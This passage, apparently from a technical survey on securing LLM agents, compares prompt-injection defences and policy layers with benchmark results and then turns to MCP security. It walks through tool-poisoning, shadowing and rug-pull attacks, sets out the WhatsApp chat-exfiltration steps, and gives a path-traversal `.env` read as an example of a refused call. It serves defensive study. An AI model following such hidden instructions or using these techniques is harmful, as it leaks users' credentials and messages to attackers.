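Stopping the run can also leak information, because anyone who notices the stop learns that the balance was high. Most tracking systems accept a leak of one bit per run, but the second flaw in CaMeL lets an attacker collect such bits without limit. When a plan fails, an ordinary Python loop outside the tracked interpreter prompts the model for another, and the new attempt starts with clean labels. Whether the policy blocked the previous attempt may depend on a secret, so an attacker who can steer the attempts could recover the whole secret bit by bit. CaMeL censors its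 error messages to reduce this risk, but without a formal guarantee.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) reaches the same conclusion about retries. In its approach, the developer's code, the retry logic and the model's programs are all written in one typed language, and a type checker examines each of the model's programs before it runs. In one example, an agent compiles a bibliography and may save only entries from a particular database. The function that saves an entry accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`, and only the function that queries the database can create such values. If the model invents an entry, its program fails the type check. Much of the enforcement therefore happens before the program runs, whereas FIDES and LLMbda check labels while the agent works.

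### What the LLMbda theorem guarantees

Garby and colleagues proved noninterference for every program in LLMbda, including programs that generate and run code, and checked the proof with the proof checker Lean. The usual definition needed adjusting because a model's answers are random and a run may never finish. The theorem therefore compares probabilities. Take two starting points that look the same to an observer, and let μ(q) and ν(q) be the probabilities that the observer sees outcome q from each. The theorem states that there is a function ω with

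μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, and Σ ω(q) ≤ 1

If both runs always finish, μ and ν each sum to 1, so both must equal ω and the observer learns nothing. Otherwise, the statistical distance between μ and ν is at most the average of the two runs' probabilities of not finishing. For example, if those probabilities are 4% and 6%, the distance is at most 5%. A run that the policy blocks counts as unfinished, so this bound also covers what an observer can learn from blocked runs.

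The theorem holds even if an attacker controls everything the model writes, because the resulting code can act only through the labelled tools. A second version of the theorem covers endorsement. Endorsing untrusted data weakens the integrity guarantee but not the guarantee for secrets, however freely a program does it.

The developer is responsible for meeting the other assumptions, including that the tool library labels every source correctly and checks labels at every sensitive sink. The proof treats all data sources as part of the program, so it does not cover a real mail server that behaves differently from its description. A separate theorem shows that the software that runs LLMbda programs matches the mathematical definition if the model's answers follow a fixed probability distribution for each conversation.

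### Results with enforcement on and off

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo in 2025. The table shows the share of tasks each agent completed with GPT-4o when it was not under attack.

| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, policies off | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic, policies on | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, policies off | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
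| FIDES, policies on | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

With the policies on, FIDES completed 8% more tasks than the basic agent on average, and 16% more when both used OpenAI's reasoning model o1. The basic agent did better only on travel tasks. Most travel tools may run in an untrusted context, so the policies didn't reduce the number of tasks it completed, whereas GPT-4o often mishandled FIDES's variables. With the policies off, FIDES completed 6.3% fewer tasks than the basic agent with o1 and 23.7% fewer with GPT-4o. Stronger models evidently cope better with hidden data, although both models are now old.

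By the researchers' count, enforcement stopped all the injections in the AgentDojo benchmark. The benchmark's own scoring recorded three successful injections against FIDES, but the researchers examined these by hand and reclassified them. Across all the agents they tested, such disputed cases included calls that the policy had blocked and Slack messages without links, which the policy allows.

The researchers' labelling made the test easier than real use. They marked a data field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, but a developer has to decide which fields are dangerous without knowing the attacks in advance. An injection in a field wrongly marked as trusted would get past the checks.

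Randori, the agent that Garby and colleagues tested on the banking tasks in 2026, is written in LLMbda. It failed twice in 1,296 attacked runs across three models, GPT-5.2, Qwen3.7-plus and MiMo-v2.5. Turning on CaMeL's policy checks roughly halved CaMeL's utility with MiMo-v2.5, from 34 to 18 of 48 task runs, much as it had with GPT-5.2. The 48 runs cover only 16 tasks, so the margins of error are around 20 percentage points. With GPT-5.2, the gap between Randori's 75% and CaMeL's 38% with checks on is large enough to take seriously, but smaller gaps are not.

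Zhou and colleagues' system lost about as much as CaMeL. Garby and colleagues report that it completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks without information-flow policies and 8 with them. Many of the lost tasks require an agent to act on untrusted data, which a strict policy forbids. Randori avoids much of this loss because its plans can endorse such data.

### How two attacks still succeeded

Both successful attacks on Randori were runs, with GPT-5.2, of the same case, in which an attacker replaces the bill that the user wants paid. LLMbda correctly labelled the file containing the bill as untrusted, and the payment tool accepts only trusted arguments. But the plan could not carry out the user's request without endorsing the payment details from the file as trusted, so the attacker's details passed the check.

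The theorem guarantees integrity only for plans that contain no endorsement, so the attacks do not contradict it. When the researchers removed the `endorse` command, the same attack failed, but so did the legitimate task. With the other two models, removing it reduced completed runs from 36 to 30 for Qwen3.7-plus and from 31 to 26 for MiMo-v2.5.

The planning model specifies what to endorse before it receives any outside data, so an attacker cannot use that data to make it add an exception during the run. The model may still write too broad an exception at the start. Garby and colleagues describe two ways to limit this. One is to forbid further endorsements by code generated from endorsed data, and the other is to allow endorsement only for values from a small set. The second limit would stop the false bill if the set contained only the accounts that the user normally pays.

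The triage assistant needs similar limits if the maintainer wants it to correct typos by itself. If the plan endorses the whole text of issue 412, a stranger can dictate the change. A narrower plan could endorse only a quarantined model's choice of one file from a list of the project's documentation files. The assistant could then run a spelling checker on that file and write the corrected version without using any of the stranger's text.

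## Writing and enforcing rules for tool calls

Labels record where a value came from, but some of the maintainer's rules concern the call itself. With Microsoft's label settings, the assistant could comment on issue 398 even though the maintainer had asked about issue 412, because the context is equally public in both cases. The reference monitor enforces such rules through its policy layer, which compares each proposed tool call with a set of written rules before the tool runs.

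The enforcement layer needs the proposed call and its arguments, the authenticated user's identity, the task, and the earlier calls. It then allows the call, refuses it, or escalates it to a person or a further check. After a refusal, the application usually sends the model an error message with the reason, so the agent can continue the user's task in another way.

Except for the proposed call itself, this information must come from a source the model cannot alter. Amazon Web Services (AWS), a cloud provider, sells a policy layer for agents. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* gives the example of a shop whose agent may offer bulk discounts only to platinum customers who order at least 50 items. The customer's tier comes from the login token, so the model cannot invent it. The quantity comes from the model's own tool call, so the layer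 can only check that it is within limits. If the rule also took the tier from the model's arguments, an injected sentence could make any customer appear to be platinum. For the same reason, the triage assistant's application should use ordinary code to extract the issue number from the maintainer's request before the model reads any issue.

### Where to put the check

| Place | What it can check | How a call can get round it |
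|---|---|---|
| Inside the agent framework | Every tool, including built-in ones, with the task and the full history | Code that the agent runs on the same machine may contact a service directly or change the rules |
| At a gateway between the agent and its tools | Calls to remote tools, with the user's identity | Built-in tools and direct network connections do not pass through the gateway |
| At the tool itself | The arguments and the current state of the data, whoever makes the call | Another tool may reach the same data, and this tool rarely has the task or the history |

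*Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) describes a rule system that works in either of the first two places. Developers can add it to the agent as a library, which takes a few lines of code and covers built-in tools. Users who cannot change the agent can instead redirect its connections through a proxy, but this does not cover built-in tools that do not use those connections.

AWS chose to enforce rules at the gateway. Its service, which *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) announced on 3 March, blocks every call that no rule allows. A security team can change the rules without changing the agent's code. If the rules would block every call to a tool, the gateway also removes that tool from the list it sends to the agent, so the model gets no information about it. These protections apply only to traffic that goes through the gateway. If the triage assistant's machine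 also stores a GitHub password, a script on that machine could use it to post comments without any check.

A check in the tool applies to every caller, but `post_comment` normally has no record of which issue the maintainer named. Developers would also have to repeat shared rules in each tool, and AWS warns that scattered checks are hard to audit. Developers can enforce rules in more than one place. For instance, the triage assistant could have a gateway with detailed rules and a GitHub credential that permits comments but not file changes.

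### Three rules for the triage assistant

Suppose the maintainer types "Triage issue 412". A small policy for this task could look like this:

```
refuse every call that no rule allows

# Rule 1: tool name
allow read_issue(number)

# Rule 2: argument
allow read_file(path)
    if full_path(path) is inside src/ or docs/

# Rule 3: order
allow post_comment(number, text)
    if number == task.issue
    and history contains read_issue(number)
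    and history does not contain post_comment
```

| Rule | Permitted call | Refused call |
|---|---|---|
| Tool name | `read_issue(412)` | `write_file("build.yml", ...)`, because no rule allows this tool |
| Argument | `read_file("src/loader.py")` | `read_file("src/../.env")`, because the full path leads to `.env` |
| Order | `post_comment(412, ...)` after `read_issue(412)` | A second `post_comment(412, ...)` in the same run |

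If `src/` and `docs/` contain no secrets, this policy prevents all three outcomes the maintainer forbade. The assistant cannot open `.env`, change a file or comment on another issue. It can still post a misleading comment on issue 412, because the rules do not restrict the comment's text.

Small errors in the checking code can let through calls that the rules forbid. Without `full_path`, the second refused call would pass, because its path begins with a permitted folder. The order rule can also fail if the model requests two comments at once, because both might pass before the history records either. The layer therefore has to check and record each call in a single step.

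### Policy languages and automatic checks

These rules are easier to check when written in a specialised language than in Python. AWS uses Cedar, an open-source language without loops or stored state. In Cedar, a rule that forbids a call overrides any rule that permits it, and the order of the rules makes no difference. Progent also gives "forbid" rules priority over "allow" rules, and it refuses any call that matches neither.

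This simplicity limits which rules Cedar can enforce on its own. It doesn't store earlier calls, so for Rule 3 the surrounding software would have to keep the history and pass the relevant facts to Cedar with each request. Progent's conditions also refer only to the arguments of the current call.

Software can translate the rules into logical formulas and find mistakes before anyone relies on them. AWS's analysis tool detects a rule that can never apply because it requires a customer to be both gold and platinum, and one that always applies because it covers orders of "at least 100 or fewer than 100". It can also compare two versions of a policy, which is useful because the effect of a change is easy to misjudge. In one of AWS's examples, a policy refuses bulk discounts on limited editions, and an administrator adds the condition that the order must exceed 200 items. This narrows the refusal,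 so an order for 73 limited-edition items now gets the discount, even though the extra condition looks stricter.

### What each kind of rule costs

Shavit tested rules on tool names, arguments and order separately. In that system, a model reads the user's request and the list of available tools before the agent starts, then writes down which tools the task needs, which argument values the request fixes and which steps must come first. Ordinary code then checks each call against this plan. Shavit ran the checks on the old GPT-4o logs also used in the comparison of AgentDojo's built-in defences.

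| Rules | Attack success | Harmless tasks with a blocked call | Harmless tasks with a blocked or flagged call |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 45.7% | | |
| Tool names | 9.6% | 16.2% | 16.2% |
| Tool names and arguments | 4.3% | 16.2% | 32.9% |
| Tool names, arguments and order | 2.0% | 31.1% | 40.4% |
| Tool names and arguments, with local reads exempt | 4.3% | 8.8% | 25.4% |

The list of tool names provides most of the protection. Rules about the order of steps add the least protection and nearly double the number of blocked tasks, because an agent often has a good reason to use a different order. At least 15% of the harmless tasks needed a tool that the plan had left out.

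The last row exempts tools that only read the user's own data, such as a calendar search. This roughly halves the number of blocked tasks without letting more attacks reach their harmful step. The exemption is safe only if the data cannot leave through the reading tool. When Shavit also exempted the tool that fetches web pages, attack success under the full set of rules rose from 2.0% to 5.8%. In the triage assistant, exempting `read_file` would expose `.env` to the model. Only the rules on `post_comment` would then protect the file, and they do not examine the comment's text.

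Shavit replayed old logs, which assumes that an agent gives up after a refusal. A live agent might find another way to reach the attacker's goal or the user's, so the table probably overstates both the gain in security and the loss of usefulness.

### Deriving rules from the user's request

Progent also has a model write the first policy from the user's request, but lets the policy change as the agent learns more. Suppose a user asks an agent to do whatever is in Alice's email titled "TODOs for the week". The first policy allows only a search for that email. The email contains instructions to summarise the user's recent emails and post the summary on Slack, which requires tools that the first policy blocks.

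After such a discovery, a model proposes a new policy. Let A(P) be the set of all tool calls that policy P allows. The new policy P′ is a narrowing if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

and an expansion otherwise. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether logical conditions can all hold together, looks for a call that P′ allows and P does not. If there is none, Progent applies the update at once. If there is one, the update needs approval, either from a person or from a setting that the developer chose in advance. An injection can make the model propose a permission to email the attacker, but the solver will recognise the proposal as an expansion.

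In tests with GPT-4o, attacks on AgentDojo succeeded 39.9% of the time without Progent and 1.0% of the time with it. On Agent Security Bench, another collection of simulated attacks, the rate dropped from 70.3% to 3.9%. Progent reduced utility only slightly on either benchmark. Shi and colleagues set the system to approve every expansion automatically, to imitate a careless user. The solver's guarantee therefore did not affect these figures, which mainly reflect how well the model wrote policies. With the first policy alone, without updates, 2.5% of attacks on AgentDojo succeeded. With a person reviewing the first policy and every expansion, no attack succeeded. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so that person would have had few to review.

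The approvals are hard to avoid because the solver cannot distinguish a useful expansion from a harmful one. The triage assistant needs approval to open the file that issue 412 leads it to, whether that file is `config/dev.yaml` or `.env`.

Li, Cao and Xiao (2026), in *ToolFence*, concentrate on attacks that keep the expected tool and change an argument, such as the recipient of a payment. Before the agent starts, a model turns the user's request into a set of permissions. Each permission fixes the tool, the number of uses and the allowed source of every sensitive argument. The value may have to appear in the user's request, or in a particular field returned by a particular tool. A call may run only if

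stage fits ∧ tool matches ∧ arguments match their sources ∧ uses left > 0

Ordinary code makes this check and reserves one use in the same step. If a task needs a permission that the first set lacks, a separate model reviews the proposed call and may add the permission. The following results are for an agent running Qwen3-max.

| Benchmark | Kind of attack | Attack success, no defence | Attack success, ToolFence | Utility without attacks, before and after |
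|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | Instructions in tool results | 21.2% | 0.0% | 66.3%, 64.3% |
| Agent Security Bench | Instructions in tool results and memory | 40.2% | 4.2% | 71.5%, 67.2% |
| MCPTox | Instructions in tool descriptions | 38.1% | 6.1% | 67.2%, 65.4% |
| AgentLAB | Long attacks spread over many steps | 76.3% | 29.4% | 62.4%, 61.1% |

ToolFence's argument checks matter most. When Li and colleagues removed them, attack success on Agent Security Bench with Llama-3.3-70B rose from 5.1% to 24.0%. Removing the ability to add permissions hardly changed attack success, but it reduced the share of tasks completed under attack from 44.3% to 35.8%. Runs took 1.63 times as long on average with ToolFence, compared with almost 13 times as long with CaMeL.

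The AgentLAB attacks did better because they spread their instructions across several records, until the harmful action looks like a necessary step. The reviewing model may then grant an overly broad permission. A rule about sources also doesn't protect against an attacker who controls the permitted source.

### Compiling rules from a company's written policy

Many organisations already have written rules, such as "customers must confirm a cancellation". *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) turns such documents into tool-call rules once, before any task begins. A model matches each sentence of the policy to a fixed vocabulary of conditions and to the tools it concerns. It does this five times, and *NOMOS* keeps the rules that appear in most attempts. Ordinary code also checks every proposed rule against the list of tools and their arguments.

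The comparison led to the repair or rejection of 29 of 79 proposed rules for an airline's policy and 7 of 53 for a shop's. The sentence "authenticate the user before any action" became a rule that blocked every tool until the user had logged in, including the two tools that perform the login, so no user could have logged in. Another proposed rule required the customer's approval even to look up a flight's status. A larger model also made such errors, including a rule that would have blocked all 14 of the airline's tools.

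Some faulty rules pass this comparison. For example, a telephone company's instruction was to check that a bill is overdue before requesting payment, but the compiler produced a rule that forbade payment requests for overdue bills. The researchers caught the error by applying the rules to recorded conversations, where this rule would have refused 47 of 49 payment requests in successful runs.

They then tested the compiled rules on τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service tasks with written policies. They counted violations using a separate, hand-written set of rules rather than the compiled ones. The share of the airline agent's changes that violated the policy fell from 66.3% without the compiled rules to 2.6% with them, and the shop agent's rate fell from 30.8% to 6.9%. Under the compiled rules, the airline agent made a third as many changes but completed 47.6% of its tasks, up from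 39.2%, since a forbidden change usually made the task fail anyway. More than half of the shop agent's remaining violations concerned two clauses that the compiler had never turned into rules.

Yu and colleagues also compared NOMOS with Progent on AgentDojo's banking tasks, using the same small open model, Gemma-4-26B.

| System | Attack success | Utility without attacks |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 46.5% | 79.2% |
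| Progent, with automatic policies | 5.6% | 62.5% |
| NOMOS | 0.0% | 70.8% |

Of the 16 attacks that succeeded against Progent, 12 occurred in two tasks in which the user asks the agent to pay a bill. The request does not name the recipient's account, so a policy derived from the request cannot restrict payment to that account, and a payment to the attacker's account is allowed. NOMOS enforces a standing rule that money may go only to recipients whom the user named or has paid before. In one of the two tasks, the rule also blocks the genuine payment, because the correct account number, like the attacker's, appears only in the bill.

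This comparison favours NOMOS somewhat. AgentDojo has no written policy, so the researchers wrote one and revised it after seeing how it affected harmless tasks. There were only 16 banking tasks, so the difference in utility between the two systems could be due to chance. In 8 of 288 attacked runs, the agent also redirected an injected payment to a recipient the user had paid before. The policy allows this, and the benchmark does not count it as a success for the attacker.

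Rules can reduce utility much more in other settings. On AgentDojo's Slack tasks, a stricter version of one rule stopped the 15 attacks that had still succeeded in 105 runs, but it reduced utility in the absence of attacks from 57.1% to 14.3%. Many of those tasks require the agent to contact people whose names it finds in what it reads, and the rule cannot distinguish them from an attacker's contacts.

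### Learning rules from past runs

*AgentGuardian* (Abaev, Klimov and colleagues, 2026) derives rules from an agent's recorded behaviour instead of having people write them. During a trial period, the software records which tools the agent uses, with what arguments and in what order. It groups similar calls and derives a rule from each group, with patterns for text arguments, ranges for numbers, and the usual working hours. It also builds a graph of the sequences it observed. Later calls have to match a learned rule and follow a path in the graph.

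The test covered a research assistant and an IT support agent. For each, the researchers learned rules from 60 harmless runs, then tested them on another 40 harmless runs and 10 with misleading inputs. The rules caught 18 of the 20 misleading runs and wrongly rejected 8 of the 80 harmless ones. With only 20 misleading runs, the true detection rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 70% to 97%. The rules also flagged six harmless runs in which the model had made a mistake, for example by inventing a file name.

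A person needs to read learned patterns because they can be too broad. Rules based on ten runs were so general that they accepted almost any text. Abaev and colleagues even present one example as limiting a tool to text files in two folders, but its last alternative matches a text file in any folder.

The method also assumes that nobody attacks during the trial period. A company can arrange this for an internal agent, but it is harder for a public repository, where a stranger can file hostile issues in those weeks and influence what the software later treats as normal. Learned rules work best for repetitive tasks. They suit the triage assistant less well, because a bug report may lead it to a file it has never opened.

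### From ordinary language to a correct policy

The checks in Cedar and NOMOS can show that a rule is well formed and can take effect, but not that it matches what its author intended. Suppose the maintainer writes "never reveal anything confidential", and a model turns this into a rule against opening `.env`. The rule names a real tool and a real file and contradicts nothing, but it does not cover a private key stored in `config/`.

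According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, a formal policy correctly translates a rule written in ordinary language only if both give the same decision in every situation the application could reach. Comparing them requires defining words such as "confidential" in terms of actual files and tools, which the original rule rarely does. Even then, ordinary language remains ambiguous, so any automatic comparison can be wrong. The paper therefore calls for translation methods with a known limit on how far the policy may differ from the rule, but no such method exists yet.

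Using a model to translate requests into rules weakens the argument for a policy layer. The layer is reliable because it always makes the same decision about the same call, under rules that people can inspect. If a model writes the rules, the decisions are only as good as its reading of the request, and nobody can prove that it will read the next one correctly. A model that judges calls during the run adds another risk, because an attacker can try to persuade it. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) makes this objection to Progent's updates. In Progent, a model first decides, without seeing the tool's result, whether an update is needed, but the model that then writes the update reads the result and has to ignore any malicious instructions in it.

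If a model writes the rules before it reads any untrusted content, it may still misunderstand the user, as with a fixed plan, but a stranger's text cannot cause the misunderstanding. Progent's attack success rate of 2.5% without policy updates shows that such rules can stop most attacks. This protection does not cover requests that contain pasted text, and an attacker can still exploit a rule that was too broad from the start.

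A judging model can also receive less information. Shavit had a model review the calls flagged under the plan, giving it the request, the plan and the earlier calls but no tool results. When the rules covered tool names and arguments and exempted local reads, the model released 7 of 28 harmless calls and none of 226 harmful ones. But it still received the arguments of each call, and an agent can copy an attacker's words into those. Shavit did not test attacks designed to persuade the model.

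It makes sense for people to write the few rules that must always hold and for a model to write the narrower rules for each task. Progent supports this by applying the fixed rules first, so a task's policy cannot permit what they forbid. The maintainer should use the fixed rules mainly to forbid things, because a fixed permission also overrides the task's policy. For example, if a fixed rule allows `read_file` in general, a task policy that excludes `.env` has no effect.

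### An adaptive test of Progent

Most of these results come from attacks that existed before the defence did. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, June 2026) tests an attack written specifically against Progent. The attack targets the model that updates the policy, by describing the harmful action as a routine step that the user has already authorised. Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, both acted as the agent and wrote the policies. The researchers used eight tasks from each of three AgentDojo settings and ran the whole test three times.

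| Setting | Attack success, no defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack | Utility under attack, no defence | Utility under adaptive attack, Progent |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% | 31.9% | 31.0% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% | 47.5% | 19.2% |
| Office | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 56.3% | 27.1% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% | 45.2% | 25.8% |

Progent withstood this attack, but mean utility fell from about 45% to 26%, and each task needed about 15 times as many model calls. In the office tasks, the agent ignored every injection even without a defence, so Progent had no attacks to prevent there, yet it halved the agent's utility. Some of the loss may be due to the small model's poor policies, since Shi and colleagues found little loss of utility with GPT-4o.

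The low attack rate is weaker evidence than it looks. The adaptive attack did worse than the standard one, probably because its mild wording also made the agent less likely to obey. It was a single hand-written template, whereas the attacks that broke twelve earlier defences went through many rounds of revision. The three repetitions used the same tasks, so their close agreement shows that the result is repeatable, but not that it applies to other models or attacks. Shi and colleagues, who developed Progent, found success rates of about 0.5% to 4.2% for their own adaptive attacks with GPT-4o. This is consistent with the new result, but they were testing their own defence.

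Narisetty and colleagues did not try an attack that uses only permitted calls. For the triage assistant, a misleading comment on issue 412 would be such an attack.

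## Connecting third-party tools

The maintainer controls the code and descriptions of the triage assistant's four tools, but many agents also use tools from other suppliers. Suppose some reporters write in Japanese, and the maintainer adds `translate`, a tool that another company runs. That company writes the tool description the model reads, receives every argument the model passes to the tool and determines what the tool returns. The connection therefore adds two sources (the description and the results) and one sink (the arguments) to the inventory.

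### How the Model Context Protocol works

Many such connections use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic introduced in November 2024. The host is the application the user works with, such as a chat program or a coding agent. A client inside the host communicates with one or more servers, which are separate programs that offer tools. A local server runs on the user's machine, and a remote server is a network service.

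The client sends a `tools/list` request to a server, which replies with each tool's name, description and parameters. The reply sometimes includes annotations, which are hints such as "this tool only reads". The host puts this text into the model's context, often in the system message. When the model outputs a tool call, the client forwards it to the right server and returns the result.

The current version of the Model Context Protocol (MCP) is 2026-07-28, named after its release date. *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (Anthropic, 2026) reports more than 400 million monthly downloads of the protocol's software libraries. The roadmap, updated on 16 November, sets 30 March 2027 as the target for the next version (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

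A model needs tool descriptions to choose a tool, so they are in its context before it starts work. Developers used to write these descriptions themselves, and models learned to follow them. With the Model Context Protocol (MCP), someone the developer does not know can write them. Under the November 2025 specification (Model Context Protocol, 2025), hosts should treat descriptions of a tool's behaviour as untrusted unless they trust the server, but a host that only forwards the text cannot make the model treat it as untrusted.

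Third-party tool descriptions weaken several of the earlier defences. A planning model that never sees a tool result still reads every tool description before it writes the plan. If the developer labels a third-party description as untrusted, the context is untrusted before the maintainer types anything, and `write_file` can never run. A hostile description can also mislead a model that derives rules from the request and the tool list, so Li and colleagues restrict ToolFence to tool definitions that the application's owner controls.

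### Poisoned and changed descriptions

On 1 April 2025, the security company Invariant Labs demonstrated the problem in its *MCP Security Notification*, using the term "tool poisoning" for hiding instructions in a tool's description. Its test tool added two numbers and had an extra parameter for a note. The description contained an instruction to read the user's private login key and a settings file, and to pass both as the note. The coding agent Cursor followed the instruction. It asked the user to confirm the call, but the dialog did not show the key. The call sent the data to the attacker's server in its arguments.

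A poisoned tool can do harm even if the agent never calls it. Invariant Labs connected Cursor to a trusted email server and to a hostile server whose description contained a false rule about where to send emails. Cursor then sent emails to the attacker, even when the user had named another recipient. This attack, which Invariant Labs calls shadowing, works because the descriptions from all connected servers share one context. The description of `translate` could likewise contain a rule that every `post_comment` call must include the contents of `.env`.

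A server can also change a tool's description after the user has approved it, so the model reads text that the user has not reviewed. Invariant Labs calls this a rug pull.

### The WhatsApp demonstration

Six days later, in Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025), the company combined shadowing with a changed description:

1. The user connects an agent to a trusted WhatsApp server and to a second server with a tool that returns a fact of the day. The user approves this tool, whose description is harmless.
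2. When the second server starts again, it supplies a different description. The client loads it without telling the user.
3. The new description contains a false technical rule that messages must go through a "proxy" number and include the user's recent chats.
4. The user asks the agent to send a message. The model calls the WhatsApp server's own sending tool, with the attacker's number as the recipient and the chat history in the text.
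5. The client asks the user to confirm. The dialog shows a phone number and what looks like a short greeting, because a long row of spaces pushes the rest out of view.
6. The user confirms, and the WhatsApp server sends the history to the attacker.

The agent never calls the fact-of-the-day tool, so running its server in a sandbox would not have prevented the theft. A client that compared descriptions would have detected the change at step 2. A rule that the recipient must come from the user's request would have blocked the call after step 4.

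In a second experiment, the attacker had no server and instead sent the user a WhatsApp message containing the instructions. The agent read it while listing chats and leaked the user's contacts. Invariant Labs found this attack slightly harder to carry out, perhaps because models are trained to give tool results less authority than tool descriptions.

### How often poisoned descriptions work

*MCPTox* (Wang, Gao and colleagues, 2025) measured this on a larger scale. It added poisoned tools to a set of 353 real tools from 45 live servers and tested 20 model configurations on 1,348 cases. An attack counted as successful only if the agent used a legitimate tool to do the harm. On average, 36.5% of attacks succeeded, and the highest rate was 72.8%, for OpenAI's o1-mini. Even the model that refused most often did so in less than 3% of cases.

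More capable models were often more vulnerable, which the researchers attribute to their being better at following instructions. These models are all old now, so the rates may not apply to current ones.

The researchers also tried using injection texts from benchmarks that place them in tool results as tool descriptions. These almost never worked. They contained only a command, while an effective description also gives a condition, such as "before any file operation", and a plausible reason. A low attack success rate on an ordinary injection benchmark is therefore weak evidence that an agent resists poisoned descriptions.

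### Skills and add-ons

A skill is a package of instructions, often with scripts, that a user installs to teach an agent a particular kind of job. Claude has skills, and the agent OpenClaw has a similar collection of add-ons called ClawHub. A reviewer cannot reject a skill just for containing instructions, since that is its purpose. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* adds that agents have no reliable way to tell where an instruction came from, whereas browsers load scripts from explicit addresses.

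*Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) compared agents with operating systems and found that only 11 of 116 standard operating-system mechanisms had a fully equivalent counterpart in agents. By default, any action that a downloaded skill leads the model to request runs with the user's full authority. Approval prompts and sandboxes can restrict the agent as a whole, but they do not give the skill less authority than the user's own request. In tests on Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI, access checks applied only to individual tools, so an agent could use the shell to write a file that the file tool had refused to write. Installing a skill therefore requires about as much trust in its author as installing a program.

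### Whose authority a call carries

What a hostile description can achieve depends on the credentials that accompany the agent's calls. For remote servers, MCP uses OAuth, a standard that lets a program act on somebody's account without their password. Suppose the triage assistant gets `read_issue` and `post_comment` from a remote MCP server that connects to GitHub:

1. The client asks an authorization server, which handles logins, for access to this MCP server. It lists the permissions it wants, called scopes, such as reading issues and posting comments.
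2. The maintainer logs in through a browser and approves. The client receives a one-time code and exchanges it for an access token. A secret that the client created beforehand stops anyone who intercepts the code from using it.
3. The model requests `post_comment(412, ...)`. The client attaches the token to this request outside the model's context.
4. The MCP server checks that the token is meant for this server and covers posting comments.
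5. The MCP server calls GitHub with a separate token, which GitHub issued for the maintainer's account.

Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026), which covers protocol version 2026-07-28, requires servers to reject tokens meant for other services and forbids them to pass the client's token on to a service such as GitHub. If services accepted each other's tokens, an attacker who took over a translation server could use the tokens it received to act on GitHub.

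A shared service account hides which user made a call. Suppose the MCP server used one GitHub account, with write access to every repository, for all users. A contributor who may only post comments could then use the server as a confused deputy to change a file, because GitHub would check only the server's permissions. With a separate GitHub token for each user, GitHub can apply that user's own permissions.

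Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* describes an attack on MCP servers that use the same client ID with another service for all their users' programs. After a user approves access once, the browser stores a cookie that records this consent. An attacker then registers their own program with the MCP server and sends the user a link. When the user clicks it, the other service detects the cookie and skips the consent page, and the MCP server sends its login code to the attacker. The guidance therefore requires MCP servers to obtain consent separately for each program.

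### Keeping credentials narrow and out of the context

The guidance recommends starting with a few low-risk scopes and requesting more when an operation needs them. However, if the server does not specify which scopes an operation needs, the client falls back to requesting every scope the server lists. The maintainer should therefore check which scopes the client received. Tokens should also expire quickly, so that a stolen one is soon useless.

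The model should never see an access token, because anything in its context can leak. Ordinary code can attach the token to requests instead. Storing tokens in a file that the agent can open is nearly as risky as showing them to the model. In Invariant Labs' test, Cursor leaked a settings file that typically holds credentials for other MCP servers.

Some identifiers have to pass through the model. According to the Model Context Protocol (2026) changelog, version 2026-07-28 removed sessions, so a server that stores data between calls, such as a shopping cart, gives the client an identifier to send back as a tool argument. This identifier can leak, so the server must not accept it as proof of who is calling. The security guidance recommends storing it with the user's identity, which the server takes from the verified token.

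Even properly secured credentials do not prevent prompt injection. The WhatsApp attack needed no stolen credentials, because the trusted server sent the message with the user's own access. A token identifies the account a call uses, but not the source of the text that led the model to make it. OAuth in MCP also assumes that a person is present to approve access in a browser. The protocol's maintainers are still working out how an agent should identify itself when it acts for an absent user or starts other agents that should have less authority.

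### How secure existing servers are

*A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (Zhou, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) found 7,973 live remote servers, 40.55% of which let anyone use their tools without authentication. Most of the open servers the researchers sampled were tests or demonstrations, but one exposed more than 5,000 customer records from a company's internal system.

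The researchers also tested 119 servers that use OAuth, and every one had at least one flaw. The sample does not represent all OAuth servers, because it includes only those that let new clients register automatically and they could test from outside. Flaws in automatic registration affected 96.6% of the sample. The protocol now discourages the registration method involved.

Servers can also have ordinary programming errors. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (2026) confirmed 24 publicly reported MCP vulnerabilities as of February 2026, most of them critical or high in severity. Common flaws let attackers run commands or open files outside the permitted folder. The count includes only reported flaws, so it does not indicate what share of servers is vulnerable.

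None of these studies measured how many servers are malicious. *MCP-in-SoS* (2026) reviews research that found malicious servers are cheap to create and hard to detect, and user studies in which many people struggled to recognise them.

A reviewed server may also disappear or lose its maintainer. In *Exposed by Design* (2026), 193 of the 464 servers in one scan were missing from the next, three days later. Zorz (2026) reports in *AI coding agents are installing MCP servers that will never be patched* that coding agents install abandoned servers that appear in their training data, some with serious flaws that nobody is fixing.

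### Pinning, registries and signatures

Pinning means storing a fingerprint of the approved tool definition and comparing it with what the server supplies later. With H as a cryptographic hash function, the client computes

fingerprint = H(name, description, parameters, annotations)

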